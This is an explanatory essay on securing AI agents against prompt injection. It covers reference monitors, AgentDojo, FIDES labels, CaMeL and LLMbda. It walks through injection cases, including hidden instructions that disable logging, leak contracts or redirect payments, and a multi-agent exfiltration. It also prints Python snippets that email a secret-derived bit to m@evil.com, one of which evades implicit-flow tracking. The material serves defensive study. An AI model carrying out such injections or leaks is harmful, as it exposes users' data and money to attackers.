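# Building security guarantees for AI systems from deterministic checks and bounded residual risk

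## What would it mean to guarantee the security of an AI agent?

An AI agent is a language model that runs in a loop and can request actions in other software, such as sending an email, searching the web or transferring money. Agent security is the study of how to keep an agent from doing harm when someone tries to turn it against its user. The main difficulty is prompt injection, in which an attacker plants text in data the agent reads so that the model treats it as an instruction. Developers have had real success training models to resist such text, but no known training method makes the resistance reliable. Another approach leaves the model unchanged and places fixed rules between it and the outside world, in the hope of proving that certain harms cannot happen whatever the model does. Much of the theory comes from work in the 1970s on military computers shared by people with different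 security clearances.

### The agent loop and the office assistant

A language model only produces text. A developer turns it into an agent by wrapping it in an ordinary program that runs a loop. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes this loop. The program keeps a conversation history, which starts with the developer's standing instructions and the user's request. It sends the whole history to the model, along with a description of each available tool. The model returns either a final reply to the user, which ends the loop, or a tool call, which is structured text that names a tool and its arguments. After a tool call, the program runs the tool, appends the result to the history and queries the model again.

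The model itself never executes anything. Costa and colleagues define a model as a function from a history and a list of tools to either a tool call or a reply. They define a tool as a function that takes the stored data and some arguments, and returns the changed data and a result. Only tools change the stored data, so a rule applied between the tool call and its execution can block any such change. They also show that the security problem arises because the program flattens the history into a single string before each query, so the model receives the user's request and a stranger's email as one run of text.

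An office assistant built this way might read its user's email, search the web, send messages and pay invoices. The attacker is someone who can send it email, which could be nearly anyone. He has no password and cannot watch the traffic between the program and the model, but he sees any message or money that reaches him. The user asks the assistant to pay the invoices that are due and summarise the rest of the inbox. One of the emails contains a paragraph addressed to the assistant.

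Depending on what that paragraph contains, the assistant might forward a confidential contract from an old attachment to the attacker. It might pay a genuine supplier's invoice into the attacker's account. Or it might give the user a false summary, saying that a client has cancelled an order when it hasn't. The false summary is by far the hardest of the three to rule out because, unlike the leak and the payment, it doesn't need a tool call. It appears in the final reply, where rules about tool calls don't apply.

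Attacks of this sort already happen outside the laboratory. In Clubic's *Une phrase cachée dans un mail suffit à manipuler une IA*, Adrien Merveille of the security firm Check Point describes a company that used agents to check its security logs for signs of intrusion. Web requests carry header fields that accept free text, and intruders used one to hide an instruction to stop logging traffic from a certain address for ten minutes. The agent complied, and the intruders later sent another hidden message telling it to return to normal. They could do this without being given access to the agent because it read text that they sent.

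### Why the designer must assume that the model can be steered

SQL injection is a similar problem. An attacker types database commands into a web form, and a careless program passes them to the database as if the programmer had written them. The fix is the parameterised query, which sends commands and data separately so that the database never interprets the data as a command. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post by David C for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, argues that language models have no equivalent fix. A model predicts the next token (a word or a fragment of one) from all the text so far, and nothing in that operation separates instructions from data. Developers can train a model to prefer instructions or mark the data with special tags, but the underlying mechanism still doesn't distinguish between the two. The post calls the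 model an "inherently confusable deputy", after the security term "confused deputy", which means a privileged program that an outsider tricks into using its privileges on the outsider's behalf.

The best case against this pessimism is that models have improved a great deal. According to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*, no attacks succeeded against Anthropic's Claude Opus 5, released in July 2026, across 129 browser scenarios. On a broader test by the security firm Gray Swan, attackers succeeded within 15 attempts 2.0% of the time. Schneier on Security's *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026) reproduces a comparison in which the rate for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol was 20.0%. The post concludes that preventing prompt injection is impossible in the general case, but that blocking it in specific cases keeps getting better.

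That seems right, but the attacker picks the case, and sending mail costs him almost nothing. If the 2.0% figure carried over to the office assistant, which nobody has shown, fifteen mails to each of a thousand companies would hijack about twenty assistants. Anthropic described a 1% attack success rate against an earlier model's browser extension as a meaningful risk. More training does not always help. Zorz (2026), in *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection*, reports research in which training on more injection attacks left agents easier to hijack, and warns that a bigger collection of attacks may contain the same attack many times. Constantin (2026), in *AI agent security*, recounts how four research teams broke AI agents in four different ways within ten days in July 2026.

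So a designer who wants a guarantee does better to start from the worst case. In *When Guardrails Aren't Enough*, a talk for the security consultancy NCC Group, Brauchler proposes imagining that a hostile person has replaced every model in the design, then working out what that person could do. In the office assistant's place, that person could read the user's mailbox, search the web, send email and make payments. The exercise replaces an open question about how language models behave with a familiar one about access rights. OpenAI, a vendor, takes much the same position in *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026), which advises companies to treat all retrieved content as untrusted and to build controls that still work when the agent is mistaken or misaligned. Assuming the worst case also gives some protection against ordinary errors, since, as Costa and colleagues note, a model can misread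 its user and make a harmful tool call with no attacker present.

### The reference monitor

The US Air Force faced a version of this problem half a century ago. It wanted to run secret and unclassified work on the same computers, for users who could write any program, and it had to assume that some of them were hostile. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) describes an expert panel's solution, which the panel called the reference monitor. This mechanism checks every attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what the program's user may do. One can picture the list as a table with a row for each user or program, a column for each thing it might reach, and the permitted operations in the cells.

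Anderson set three conditions, and a mechanism that misses any of them cannot count as secure.

- It must always be invoked. Later writers call this complete mediation: no action can reach its target without passing the check.
- It must be tamper-proof, since an attacker who can alter the check can switch it off.
- It must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely, because otherwise nobody can know that it gives the right verdict in every case.

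These conditions are harder to meet than they look. Anderson applied them to a commercial machine of the day, the HIS 635 with its GCOS III operating system. The hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory. But a program had to call the operating system to read or write a file, and most of the operating system ran with that confinement suspended, so the hardware check was not always invoked. If the operating system itself is counted as the check, then the check was between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions long, far too many for anyone to verify, and testers had broken into it several times.

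An agent's monitor naturally belongs between the model's request and the program's execution of it. A deterministic check at that point is a fixed rule, outside the model, that always gives the same verdict for the same input. For example, a rule might allow payments only to accounts on the approved supplier list. Complete mediation fails if the agent can also open the bank's website in a browser and enter a transfer there, and tamper-proofing fails if the agent can edit the supplier list.

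The size condition rules out the popular shortcut of having a second language model review each tool call, because nobody can analyse a large neural network completely. The reviewer also reads text that the attacker may have influenced. Brauchler classes such guardrails as statistical measures that are useful as an extra layer but never as a boundary. OpenAI likewise says that a review model can recommend human review but should never be the only protection against an effect that must not happen automatically.

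### The trusted base

A security check depends on other components. Anderson observed that if the monitor is suspended for some group of programs, those programs become part of the security apparatus and must meet the same standards of tamper-resistance and verifiability. The trusted base is the set of all components whose failure can void a guarantee. They are called "trusted" because the designer must rely on them, not because they are necessarily trustworthy.

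For the supplier-list rule, the trusted base includes the check's code, the list itself and anyone allowed to edit the list. It also includes the program that runs the loop, which must execute only approved calls, the operating system beneath it, and the bank's interface, which must pay the account that the check approved. An attacker who controls any of these parts does not need to defeat the check. Anderson's panel listed similar assumptions for its own design: reliable identification of users, physical protection of the equipment, protected communications and working hardware.

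Whether the model belongs to the trusted base depends on the guarantee. Costa and colleagues list it among the components they assume to be trusted, along with the system messages and tool descriptions. They mean that the attacker has not tampered with the agent's configuration; they still expect malicious mail to steer the model's output. The supplier-list rule holds whatever the model outputs, so the model can stay outside the trusted base for that rule. But the model writes the summaries, so unless something else can compare them with the mail, a guarantee that they are true depends on a component that malicious mail can steer.

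### Two kinds of claim

Suppose the check works and the company wants to tell its auditors how safe the assistant is. It can offer a proof or a measurement, which people often confuse.

A proof establishes that, under certain assumptions, a specific harm does not occur for any attacker of a given kind. Cryptography is the model for such claims. Villa, Kohno and colleagues (2026), in *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI*, recall that early ciphers rested on plausible arguments and were considered secure until somebody broke them. Cryptographers now define security using a game between a system and an adversary. The system is secure if every adversary with realistic computing power has only a negligible advantage in the game, and the proof shows that winning would mean solving a well-studied mathematical problem. The supplier-list rule needs a much simpler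 argument. Its verdict depends only on the account number and the list, so the argument covers every possible email, including attacks nobody has thought of yet.

A proof covers a harm only as the rule defines it. OpenAI gives the example of an invoice agent that notices a software subscription is lapsing and tries to renew it. The vendor and the amount are both within the rules, but the company has never agreed to sign a new contract.

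The attack success rate is the measured share of attacks, made in a particular way on a particular system, that reached their goal. Measuring it requires no theory of the system, and it can catch a programming error excluded by a proof's assumptions. But it covers only the attacks that somebody tried. Anderson made this point about the "tiger teams" that the military hired to break into its computers. A successful break-in reveals a flaw, but after an unsuccessful one, he wrote, all that anyone can state is that the security of the system is unknown.

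The success rate of attacks on the same model can vary widely between test settings. VentureBeat compared results that Anthropic published in February 2026 for Claude Opus 4.6. In a restricted coding environment, all 200 injection attempts failed. When the model operated a graphical interface with extended reasoning and no extra safeguards, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time, and the rate rose to 78.6% by the 200th attempt. With safeguards, the rate after 200 attempts was still 57.1%.

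### AgentDojo

Many of the measurements in this field come from one benchmark, *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024). It simulates four workplaces: an office suite with email, calendar and files; the messaging service Slack; a travel agency; and a bank. Each has working tools and invented data. The benchmark includes 97 user tasks, such as paying a bill from a file, and 27 injection tasks, which are an attacker's goals, such as sending as much money as possible to the attacker's account or mailing him a security code. Pairing each user task with each injection task from the same workplace gives 629 test cases.

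In each case, the benchmark places the attacker's text somewhere an outsider could plausibly have put it, such as the body of an email, and where the agent will encounter it while doing the user's task. A fixed function then inspects the state of the simulated workplace to check whether the agent transferred the money or sent the message. Debenedetti and colleagues avoided using a language model as the judge because an injection that fools the agent might also fool the judge.

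The benchmark measures three things. Benign utility is the share of user tasks that the agent completes when there is no attack. Utility under attack is the share of test cases in which the agent completes the user's task correctly, with no harmful side effects, despite the injection. The targeted attack success rate is the share of test cases in which the attacker achieves their goal. A low attack success rate can make a weak model look more secure than it is. In the original experiments, more capable models were often easier to attack, probably because weaker models followed the injected instructions but failed to complete the attacker's task.

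The 2024 scores are out of date, but the benchmark is still in use. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) counts over 900 combinations of user and injection tasks in it, and *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks* (2026) uses it to compare 13 models from six providers. *StepGuard* (2026) pairs it with a newer benchmark, AgentDyn, which has longer tasks and includes third-party instructions that the agent should follow. Such instructions matter for the office assistant because an invoice is a third party's request for payment.

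### The proposal

The proposal is to prove what can be proved, and to cap or measure the rest. If a fixed rule can describe a harm, such as a payment to an unlisted account, the designer puts a deterministic check where every action of that kind must pass it, and proves that the check excludes the harm whatever the model outputs. If no rule can exclude a harm without also blocking honest work, the designer sets a cap, such as a daily limit on payments, which turns an open-ended loss into a known maximum. For the remaining harms, including the false summary, testers attack the system as hard as they can and report how often they succeed. The residual risk is the harm still possible with the checks in place, through permitted actions or failed assumptions, and the hope is to quantify it so that a company can decide whether to accept it. How much can be proved depends on what information the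 checks use. A rule based only on the account number cannot distinguish an account the user chose from one that came from a stranger's email, so the most developed proposals label each piece of data with its origin and consult the labels before every action.

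## What does tracking the origin of data guarantee?

Information-flow control is the standard name for this kind of labelling. The labels record where the data came from and who may read it, and the program carries them along as it works. Dorothy Denning published the underlying mathematics in 1976. The best-developed version for agents is FIDES (Flow Integrity Deterministic Enforcement System), which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft. If the labels are right and the rules cover every tool, FIDES can guarantee that a stranger's text never triggers a consequential action, and that confidential data never goes directly to someone who isn't entitled to it. It can't guarantee that what the agent tells its user is true.

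### Labels and how they combine

In Denning's scheme, as *SPA* (2026) summarises it, every value belongs to a security class, and information may flow from one class to another only if their ordering permits it. A FIDES label has an integrity part, which is either trusted or untrusted, and a confidentiality part. The confidentiality part can be as simple as public or secret, but a list of permitted readers is more useful.

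The ordering, written ⊑, runs from less restrictive to more restrictive. Trusted ⊑ untrusted, because trusted text may go anywhere untrusted text may go, but not the reverse. A list of readers comes below any shorter list it contains, because fewer people may see data with the shorter list.

When a program combines two pieces of data, the result gets the join of their labels, written ⊔. The join is the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as both, so trusted ⊔ untrusted is untrusted. For reader lists, the join is the intersection, because only someone who may read both sources may read something derived from both. A lattice is an ordered set in which joins (and meets, their opposite, which FIDES doesn't need) always exist. The program therefore has a single label to check for each message, however many sources went into it.

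Microsoft's *Information-flow control* gives an example from an inbox. Alex asks an agent to answer his unanswered mail. Priya has sent him a preview of the quarterly sales, so that mail has the readers {Alex, Priya}. Marco, who isn't allowed to see the numbers yet, has also written, and his mail has the readers {Alex, Marco}. An agent that has read both drafts a reply, whose label is

{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}.

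Marco isn't on the list, so the agent may not send him the reply on its own authority. If Priya had copied Marco on her email, the intersection would be {Alex, Marco} and the reply could go out. This example involves no attacker, only an agent that would have shared too much while trying to help.

### One turn of the labelled loop

Costa and colleagues add labels to the ordinary agent loop as follows.

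1. The program appends the newest message to the conversation history and joins the message's label to the history's label.
2. It sends the history to the model and gives the model's output the label of everything the model received.
3. If the output is a tool call, the program compares the labels on the call and on each argument with the policy for that tool. If the call fails, the tool does not run.
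4. If the tool runs, its result gets the join of the labels on the call, the arguments and any stored data that the tool may have read. Anything the tool may have written gets the same label.

FIDES deliberately uses a crude rule for model output, treating all of it as influenced by everything in the history. Older systems for tracking data follow individual values through a computer's memory. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) explains that this fails here because a model may rewrite or summarise a text, or choose its next tool call based on it, without copying any value that a tracker could follow. The FIDES rule can never miss an influence, but one untrusted mail makes the whole rest of the conversation untrusted.

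Costa and colleagues mention a less restrictive method, by Siddiqui and others, which looks for a subset of the messages that is enough to produce a similar answer and then regenerates the answer from that subset alone. *APPA* (2026) keeps the crude rule, and when a check blocks a call, it searches for permitted steps that would let the work continue.

### The two policies

A consequential action is one that changes something that matters, such as a payment or a deletion. Under the trusted-action rule, the program allows a call that takes such an action only if the join of the integrity labels on the call and all its arguments is trusted. Under the permitted-reader rule, it allows a call that sends data out only if every recipient is on the data's list of readers.

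On its own, the trusted-action rule stops injected text from causing an action, but it lets an agent that has read only trusted text send a secret to anyone. Costa and colleagues accept this in some settings, reasoning that the user presumably wanted a disclosure made in a trusted context. Declassification is a deliberate exception that treats secret data as public, and it is "robust" when an attacker cannot trigger it.

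The permitted-reader rule limits what an injection can disclose, but on its own it does not stop the injection from steering the agent. The attacker could still make the office assistant send a confidential contract to the lawyer who drafted it, but could not have it sent to himself. The rule also does not prevent deletions, because they send no data to anyone.

If a tool must satisfy both rules, injected text can't trigger the call and the data can't reach the wrong person. Some of the policies that Microsoft has tested and published are looser. They allow a message if its recipients may read it *or* if the context is trusted. An injection still can't cause a leak, because it makes the context untrusted and the permitted-reader rule must then be met. But an honest mistake can cause one. For example, if Alex's system counts mail from colleagues as trusted, the looser policy would let the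 agent send Priya's figures to Marco.

### The office assistant's inbox

The user's request to pay the invoices and summarise the inbox is labelled trusted and public. The assistant then reads the mail. Each message body is labelled untrusted, and its permitted readers are its sender and recipients. The history therefore becomes untrusted too, and the user is its only permitted reader because no outsider received all of the messages.

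Suppose the attacker's paragraph takes complete control of the model. A call that mails the old contract to the attacker fails both rules, because the context is untrusted and the attacker is not a permitted reader. A transfer to his account fails the trusted-action rule, and both calls fail however he words the paragraph.

The false summary reaches the user because FIDES checks only tool calls. The reply carries an untrusted label, which an interface could display, but users would probably soon ignore a warning that appeared on every inbox summary.

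The legitimate payment also fails. The assistant has to read untrusted mail to determine what is due, and the trusted-action rule blocks every payment after that.

### Explicit secrecy

Costa and colleagues state the confidentiality guarantee as explicit secrecy, a property they take from earlier work on tracking data in ordinary programs. Let *d*₁ be the contents of the agent's data store, some public and some secret. The tool calls the agent makes when it runs on *d*₁ together form a function *g* that turns one state of the store into another. Explicit secrecy requires that *g*(*d*₁) and *g*(*d*₂) have the same public contents for any store *d*₂ that has the same public contents as *d*₁ but different secrets.

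Under this property, nothing public changes if someone replays the same actions with different secrets. A tool call that copies the contract file to a public web page violates the property, because a different contract would produce a different page.

The labelled loop satisfies this property because if two stores have the same public contents before a step, they still do after it. Querying the model does not change the store. A tool call can write to a public place only if the data it uses is public. Two stores with the same public contents supply the same public data, so the call writes the same thing in both. The same is true of each later call. This argument assumes that every tool correctly declares what it may read and write. It also requires the permitted-reader rule without the exception for trusted contexts, since that exception exists to let secrets out.

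The formal definition is narrower than this explanation suggests because it treats the conversation history as part of the program, not the store. If the model has already read a secret and copied it into an argument, the argument is a constant in *g*, and replaying the run with a different secret changes nothing. The definition alone therefore doesn't rule out this leak, but the labels cover it because the argument inherits the history's label.

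Costa and colleagues also acknowledge that the property does not limit what an observer can infer from the agent's choice of actions, because it holds the sequence of actions fixed. Suppose the assistant reads a confidential contract and looks up the dollar exchange rate only if the contract is in dollars. The lookup contains no text from the contract, and a policy might well treat lookups as harmless, but whoever runs the exchange-rate site could learn the currency. The model also leaves out timing and the length of network packets.

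The definition also assumes that the model is deterministic, meaning that the same input always produces the same output, but commercial models usually pick their words partly at random. Treating the random draws as an extra input, fixed in advance, would probably repair the argument, as long as the secrets don't affect the draws.

A stronger property, noninterference, would also cover the choice of actions. It requires that changing the secrets changes nothing an outside observer can see. Costa and colleagues reject it as too restrictive. The model chooses each action after reading the whole history, so once a secret is in the history, any later public action might depend on it. Enforcing noninterference would mean forbidding every tool that may write somewhere public after any tool that may have read a secret. For example, the office assistant could not send an outside email after opening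 the mailbox. Noninterference has been proved for agents that plan differently.

### Hidden variables and the quarantined model

FIDES lets the agent do more by keeping untrusted text out of the history. When a tool returns a result, the program checks each field's label separately. If the label is more restrictive than the history's, the program stores the field's text in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name, so the history stays trusted. For example, the model might see that an email arrived on Tuesday, with "body-3" in place of its text.

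The model can still use the text without seeing it by putting the name "body-3" into a tool call. The program fills in the text, with its label, just before the check. The call is then trusted even though one of its arguments is not, which allows finer policies. For example, a policy for sending messages can require that the recipient comes from a trusted context but let the body contain anything.

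Forwarding an email works this way, but summarising one doesn't, because a model has to read it. FIDES passes the email to a quarantined model, a separate model instance that reads untrusted data and cannot call tools. Simon Willison proposed this separation in 2023. FIDES stores the summary in a new variable, which is also untrusted. An injection can still ruin the summary, for instance by making it blank, but it can't make the quarantined model send email.

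Costa and colleagues call a task data-independent if one fixed sequence of tool calls and one final reply would solve it whatever the data contains. Sending the top three mails to a colleague is an example. The task "If one of them asks for a meeting, put it in the calendar" is data-dependent, because the agent must read the mail before it can choose its next step. The agent can open the variable that holds the mail, but then the history becomes untrusted and the check blocks consequential actions again.

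As a compromise, the planner can send the quarantined model a constrained question, such as whether there is a meeting request, and the software restricts the answer to true or false. The label records that the answer is a single bit, and a policy may endorse it, which means deliberately treating untrusted data as trusted. One bit can't hold a set of instructions, but the attacker may still be able to choose the answer, so a designer should endorse it only if both answers would be tolerable.

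With these additions, the assistant can summarise the inbox and keep its history trusted. Whether it can pay an invoice depends on the exact policy. Suppose the user asks the assistant to pay the invoice in a particular mail. The decision to pay is trusted, but the amount and the account number come from the mail. The trusted-action rule as stated above blocks the payment because it covers the arguments. In their experiments, Costa and colleagues used a weaker version that checks the call and ignores the arguments. That version would allow the payment, but it would also allow a payment to an attacker who had sent a convincing false invoice. To prevent this, a designer has to require that the account number come from a trusted source, either the user or an approved list.

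### Results on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on the AgentDojo benchmark with OpenAI's GPT-4o and o1. Both models are long out of date, so the figures are historical. AgentDojo doesn't label data as trusted or untrusted, so the team marked a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it. The test therefore covers the checks but not the labelling, because no attack could arrive through a field wrongly marked as trusted.

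The policies varied by tool. Payments, deletions and password changes required a trusted call. Emails and Slack messages required either permitted readers or a trusted call. A message with an untrusted link failed the reader test because a link can carry data to whoever runs the site. Adding people to a calendar event required both permitted readers and a trusted call.

Without checks, AgentDojo scored 160 attacks as successful against a basic GPT-4o agent. Hidden variables and the quarantined model cut this to 23 even with the checks switched off. With the checks on, AgentDojo still scored 3 successes against FIDES, but Costa and colleagues inspected the cases by hand and put the true number at zero. They excluded calls that the policy had blocked, actions that the policy allows, and attacks that only changed the wording of a reply. The zero therefore means that no attack broke the policies,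 which is all the design guarantees. Attackers may still have got some of what they wanted without breaking them.

The agents completed considerably fewer user tasks with the protection. The table shows the percentage of tasks each agent completed when there was no attack.

| Workplace | GPT-4o, basic, no checks | GPT-4o, basic, with checks | GPT-4o, FIDES, with checks | o1, basic, no checks | o1, basic, with checks | o1, FIDES, with checks |
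|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Office suite | 75.0 | 37.0 | 59.0 | 70.0 | 48.0 | 64.5 |
| Travel | 70.0 | 73.0 | 41.0 | 82.0 | 75.0 | 68.0 |
| Bank | 98.8 | 37.5 | 52.5 | 96.2 | 37.5 | 56.2 |
| Slack | 93.3 | 20.0 | 47.6 | 87.6 | 17.1 | 54.3 |

Averaged over the four workplaces, FIDES completed 8 percentage points more of the tasks than the basic agent with checks when both used GPT-4o, and 16 points more when both used o1. It completed about 34 points fewer than an unprotected agent with GPT-4o, and 23 fewer with o1. Part of this loss came from models confusing variable names or making unnecessary calls, which a better model can fix. But many of the banking failures occurred because the policy worked as intended. Those tasks told the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which a label check can't distinguish from an injection.

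### Counting approvals

Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) argue in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* that this comparison is unfair to FIDES. It compares an agent that is not allowed to ask for help with one that acts without permission, whereas real products usually ask the user before a consequential action. The researchers propose measuring how much an agent can do before it has to ask.

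On AgentDojo with GPT-5, an agent without labels that had to ask for approval of every consequential action finished 35.1% of tasks without asking. FIDES finished 57.1%, and Prudentia, the team's extension of FIDES, finished 72.7%. Prudentia tells the model about the labels and policies so that the model can plan around them. With unlimited approvals, the three completed 72.3%, 78.9% and 80.0%. The extra planning uses more tokens. With the smaller o4-mini, Prudentia used about 32,000 input tokens on an average banking task, against about 5,400 for FIDES, although most of these came from a cache.

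Prudentia can also prompt the user to endorse a whole mail. If a mail contains a list of ten jobs, one endorsement replaces ten approvals, but security then depends on the user reading the mail carefully. If the user overlooks a hostile paragraph and endorses the mail, that paragraph counts as trusted and can influence everything that follows. Kolluri and colleagues counted approvals on harmless runs and assumed that a person would refuse harmful requests. They acknowledge that people who see too many prompts start to approve them without reading.

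### Where the labels come from

The AgentDojo attacks were fixed texts, which a model might ignore even without a defence. In *SPIDES*, Zverev, Kim and colleagues (2026) tested agents that operate a web browser more harshly, by letting the attacker choose the model's output whenever the model's input contained untrusted text. This is close to the worst case, in which the attacker has replaced the model. All 56 attacks failed against each of five recent models, and the agents completed between 67.1% and 86.1% of the ordinary tasks. Under the same conditions, SOPGuard, a rival defence that asks for approval when data crosses from one website to another, let through between 53.2% and 73.2% of attacks.

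Labels are hard to get on the web. An email has a sender and recipients, but a shop's page mixes the shop's own prices with strangers' reviews and the customer's saved card, and only the shop knows which is which. SPIDES relies on website operators to mark these parts in the page's code. Zverev and colleagues built 28 websites with the marks already in place. On a site that the user trusts, an unmarked element counts as trusted and public, so if a shop forgets to mark its reviews, the agent treats any reviewer's text as trusted.

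### Implementations in 2026

Microsoft and GitHub have begun to put these ideas into products. The GitHub MCP server, which gives agents access to GitHub through a common standard called the Model Context Protocol, can now label its results if the user turns the feature on. Microsoft explains that the server labels files and issues from public repositories as public and untrusted, and those from private repositories as private and trusted. This stops a known attack in which a stranger writes a public issue telling the agent to post material from a private repository. But the labels are coarse, so a stranger's text becomes trusted if an employee pastes it into a private repository.

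GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent for the command line, has an experimental setting that keeps a label for the whole conversation and checks calls against it. So far the checks cover only selected tools from the GitHub MCP server, so the setting falls short of complete mediation. To extend coverage, Microsoft offers a gateway that sits in front of other servers, but for each tool someone must describe the output, write a function that passes on the labels, and write or choose a policy. *SPA* warns that, in general, when rules are written tool by tool, the guarantee depends on every rule being correct and complete.

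Developers who build their own agents can use Microsoft Agent Framework, which includes labels, checks, hidden variables and a quarantined model. These features are experimental and work only in Python. The framework uses three confidentiality levels (public, private and user identity) instead of the research version's list of readers, so it cannot distinguish Priya from Marco.

Developers also have to label their own data sources, and Microsoft has published two different defaults for tools left unlabelled. *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026), Microsoft's release post from May, gives the default as trusted and public. Microsoft's documentation for the framework gives it as untrusted and public, and describes this as failing closed. That is true for integrity but not for confidentiality, because an unlabelled secret counts as public under either default. Both pages use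 the example of an agent that an attacker tricks into reading a file of passwords and posting it as a public comment. The framework blocks the comment because the developer has labelled the file's contents as private. Without that label, the confidentiality check would let the passwords through.

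## Can the guarantee be proved for agents that write and run their own code?

The FIDES theorem covers one fixed loop in which the model requests one tool call at a time. Some other agents answer a request by writing a whole program and running it, so a proof about them has to hold for any program the model might write. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) give such a proof in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* for LLMbda, a small programming language they designed for agents. They prove a form of noninterference, a property FIDES's designers had rejected as too restrictive. The guarantee therefore covers leaks through the agent's choice of actions as well as direct copying. The proof takes the labels and policies as given. It also allows programs to mark untrusted data as trusted, and the only two attacks that succeeded in the team's tests depended on this.

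### CaMeL

LLMbda grew out of problems with an earlier system, CaMeL (Capabilities for Machine Learning), which Google DeepMind introduced in 2025. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe how it works. A privileged model, the planner, reads the user's request and writes a program in a restricted form of Python. A quarantined model, like the one in FIDES, reads untrusted data when the program asks it to. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program and makes the tool calls. If the office assistant worked this way and the user asked it to pay the latest invoice from a supplier called Acme, the plan might be:

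```
mail = find_email("Acme invoice")
bill = ask_quarantined("Extract the account and the amount", mail)
send_money(bill.account, bill.amount)
```

The planner writes all three lines before any model has read the mail, so an injection in the mail can't add a fourth line. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) calls this property control-flow integrity. It means that the agent makes only the tool calls in a plan that depends only on trusted information, although untrusted data may determine which of the plan's branches runs.

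An injection can also change the account number that the quarantined model extracts. CaMeL's interpreter therefore tags every value with its sources and its permitted readers. CaMeL calls these tags capabilities, but they are labels like those in FIDES, not tokens that grant access. Before each tool call, a policy written as a short Python function checks the tool, the arguments and their tags, and allows or denies the call. For example, a payment policy could require the account number to come from the company's supplier list, which would block the plan above and force the planner to look Acme up.

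CaMeL had no soundness theorem, and its designers called formalisation a crucial direction for further work. In *Operationalizing CaMeL*, Tallam and Miller (2025) recommended a machine-checked proof that secrets cannot affect public outputs except through approved channels. Garby and colleagues studied the interpreter and found two leaks that would have made such a proof impossible.

### The assignment that never runs

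Suppose a policy forbids any outgoing email that depends on the user's bank balance. CaMeL blocks the obvious attempt to get round it:

```
if balance > threshold: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The email doesn't contain the balance, but its arrival reveals whether the balance is high. Security researchers call this an implicit flow. CaMeL catches it by attaching a label, called the program-counter label, to the program's current position. Inside the branch, that label is set to "secret", so the email fails the check.

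A longer program with two extra variables gets past the same defence:

```
rich = True
maybe = True
if balance > threshold: maybe = False
if maybe: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the third line sets "maybe" to false and labels it secret. The assignment on the fourth line then doesn't run, so "rich" stays true and public, and the email goes out. If the balance is low, the assignment on the third line doesn't run, so "maybe" stays true and public. The fourth line then sets "rich" to false, and no email goes out. In both cases, "rich" is labeled public, but its value reveals whether the balance is high.

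Garby and colleagues trace this classic example to J. S. Fenton's work in the 1970s. The tracker labels a variable when an assignment changes it, but here the information comes from an assignment that did not happen. The standard remedy is to stop the program whenever a branch that depends on a secret would change a public variable. With that rule, a high balance would stop the program at the third line. Anyone who can see that the program stopped still learns that the balance is high, but most systems of this kind allow a leak of about that size.

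An attacker who can only send mail doesn't write CaMeL's plans, and an honest planner has no reason to write this one. The flaw becomes dangerous if the attacker's text reaches the planner or a hostile person has replaced the planner.

### Where the tracking stops

CaMeL's interpreter runs inside an ordinary Python loop. When a plan fails, the loop calls the planner again with information about the error. Nothing tracks this information, so each new attempt starts with clean labels even though it depends on what happened in the last one.

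Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can leak one bit. The loop lets a program make many attempts. The first could test one binary digit of the balance, the second could test the next digit, and so on. Twenty attempts would recover any whole number up to about a million. CaMeL censors error messages to reduce this risk, but this gives no formal guarantee.

Garby and colleagues also found that inserting untrusted text into a fixed string made the result count as trusted. Tallam and Miller list further channels that the labels don't cover, including how long a program runs and how many times it contacts a public server.

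Tracking can also stop where one agent hands work to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three CaMeL agents and asked it to send a colleague a summary of job applicants on Slack. An attacker had planted text in the applicant database. A coordinating agent fetched the records from a database agent, had its quarantined model summarise them, and put the summary into an instruction to a notification agent. The notification agent treated that instruction as a trusted user request, so its planner read the planted text and added an email that sent the applicants' details to the attacker. The coordinating and database agents followed the same plans as they would have without the attack.

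The team ran these agents without data policies to test control-flow integrity alone. Their remedy sends trusted instructions and untrusted values between agents through separate channels. On their benchmark, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent separately, and 0.0% with the separate channels. The benchmark's attacks therefore seldom exploited the gap, but the Slack example shows that a system can still be vulnerable when each of its agents is protected individually.

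### LLMbda

Garby and colleagues start from the lambda calculus, a language built from functions, which theorists like because it has few rules to reason about. Their language, LLMbda, adds operations for interacting with a language model and attaches a label to every value. In the simplest version, a label is a subset of {U, S}, where U means untrusted and S means secret. The empty set means trusted and public, and the join of two labels is their union.

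Every rule in the language passes labels on. Even a constant carries the label S if it appears inside a branch that depends on a secret. This covers the case that explicit secrecy missed, in which the office assistant looks up the dollar exchange rate only if a confidential contract is in dollars. In LLMbda, the lookup's arguments would carry the label S, so the program would stop if the lookup tool accepted only public arguments.

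The conversation with the model has a label too, which covers every message in it. Four operations act on the conversation:

- **send** adds a message.
- **recv** samples a reply from the model and, if the reply is code, runs it.
- **fork** carries out some steps on a temporary copy of the conversation and then restores the original.
- **clear** empties the conversation.

Any code in a reply runs with the conversation's label as its program-counter label, so everything it computes is at least as restricted as the text that influenced it. The proof does not depend on what code an attacker might get the model to write.

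A programmer can use these operations to build a quarantined model. The program forks the conversation, clears the copy, sends it a question about an untrusted email and returns the answer. The answer carries the label U, while the main conversation stays trusted because it never contains the email. CaMeL and FIDES build this separation into their design, whereas an LLMbda program can use it wherever it is needed.

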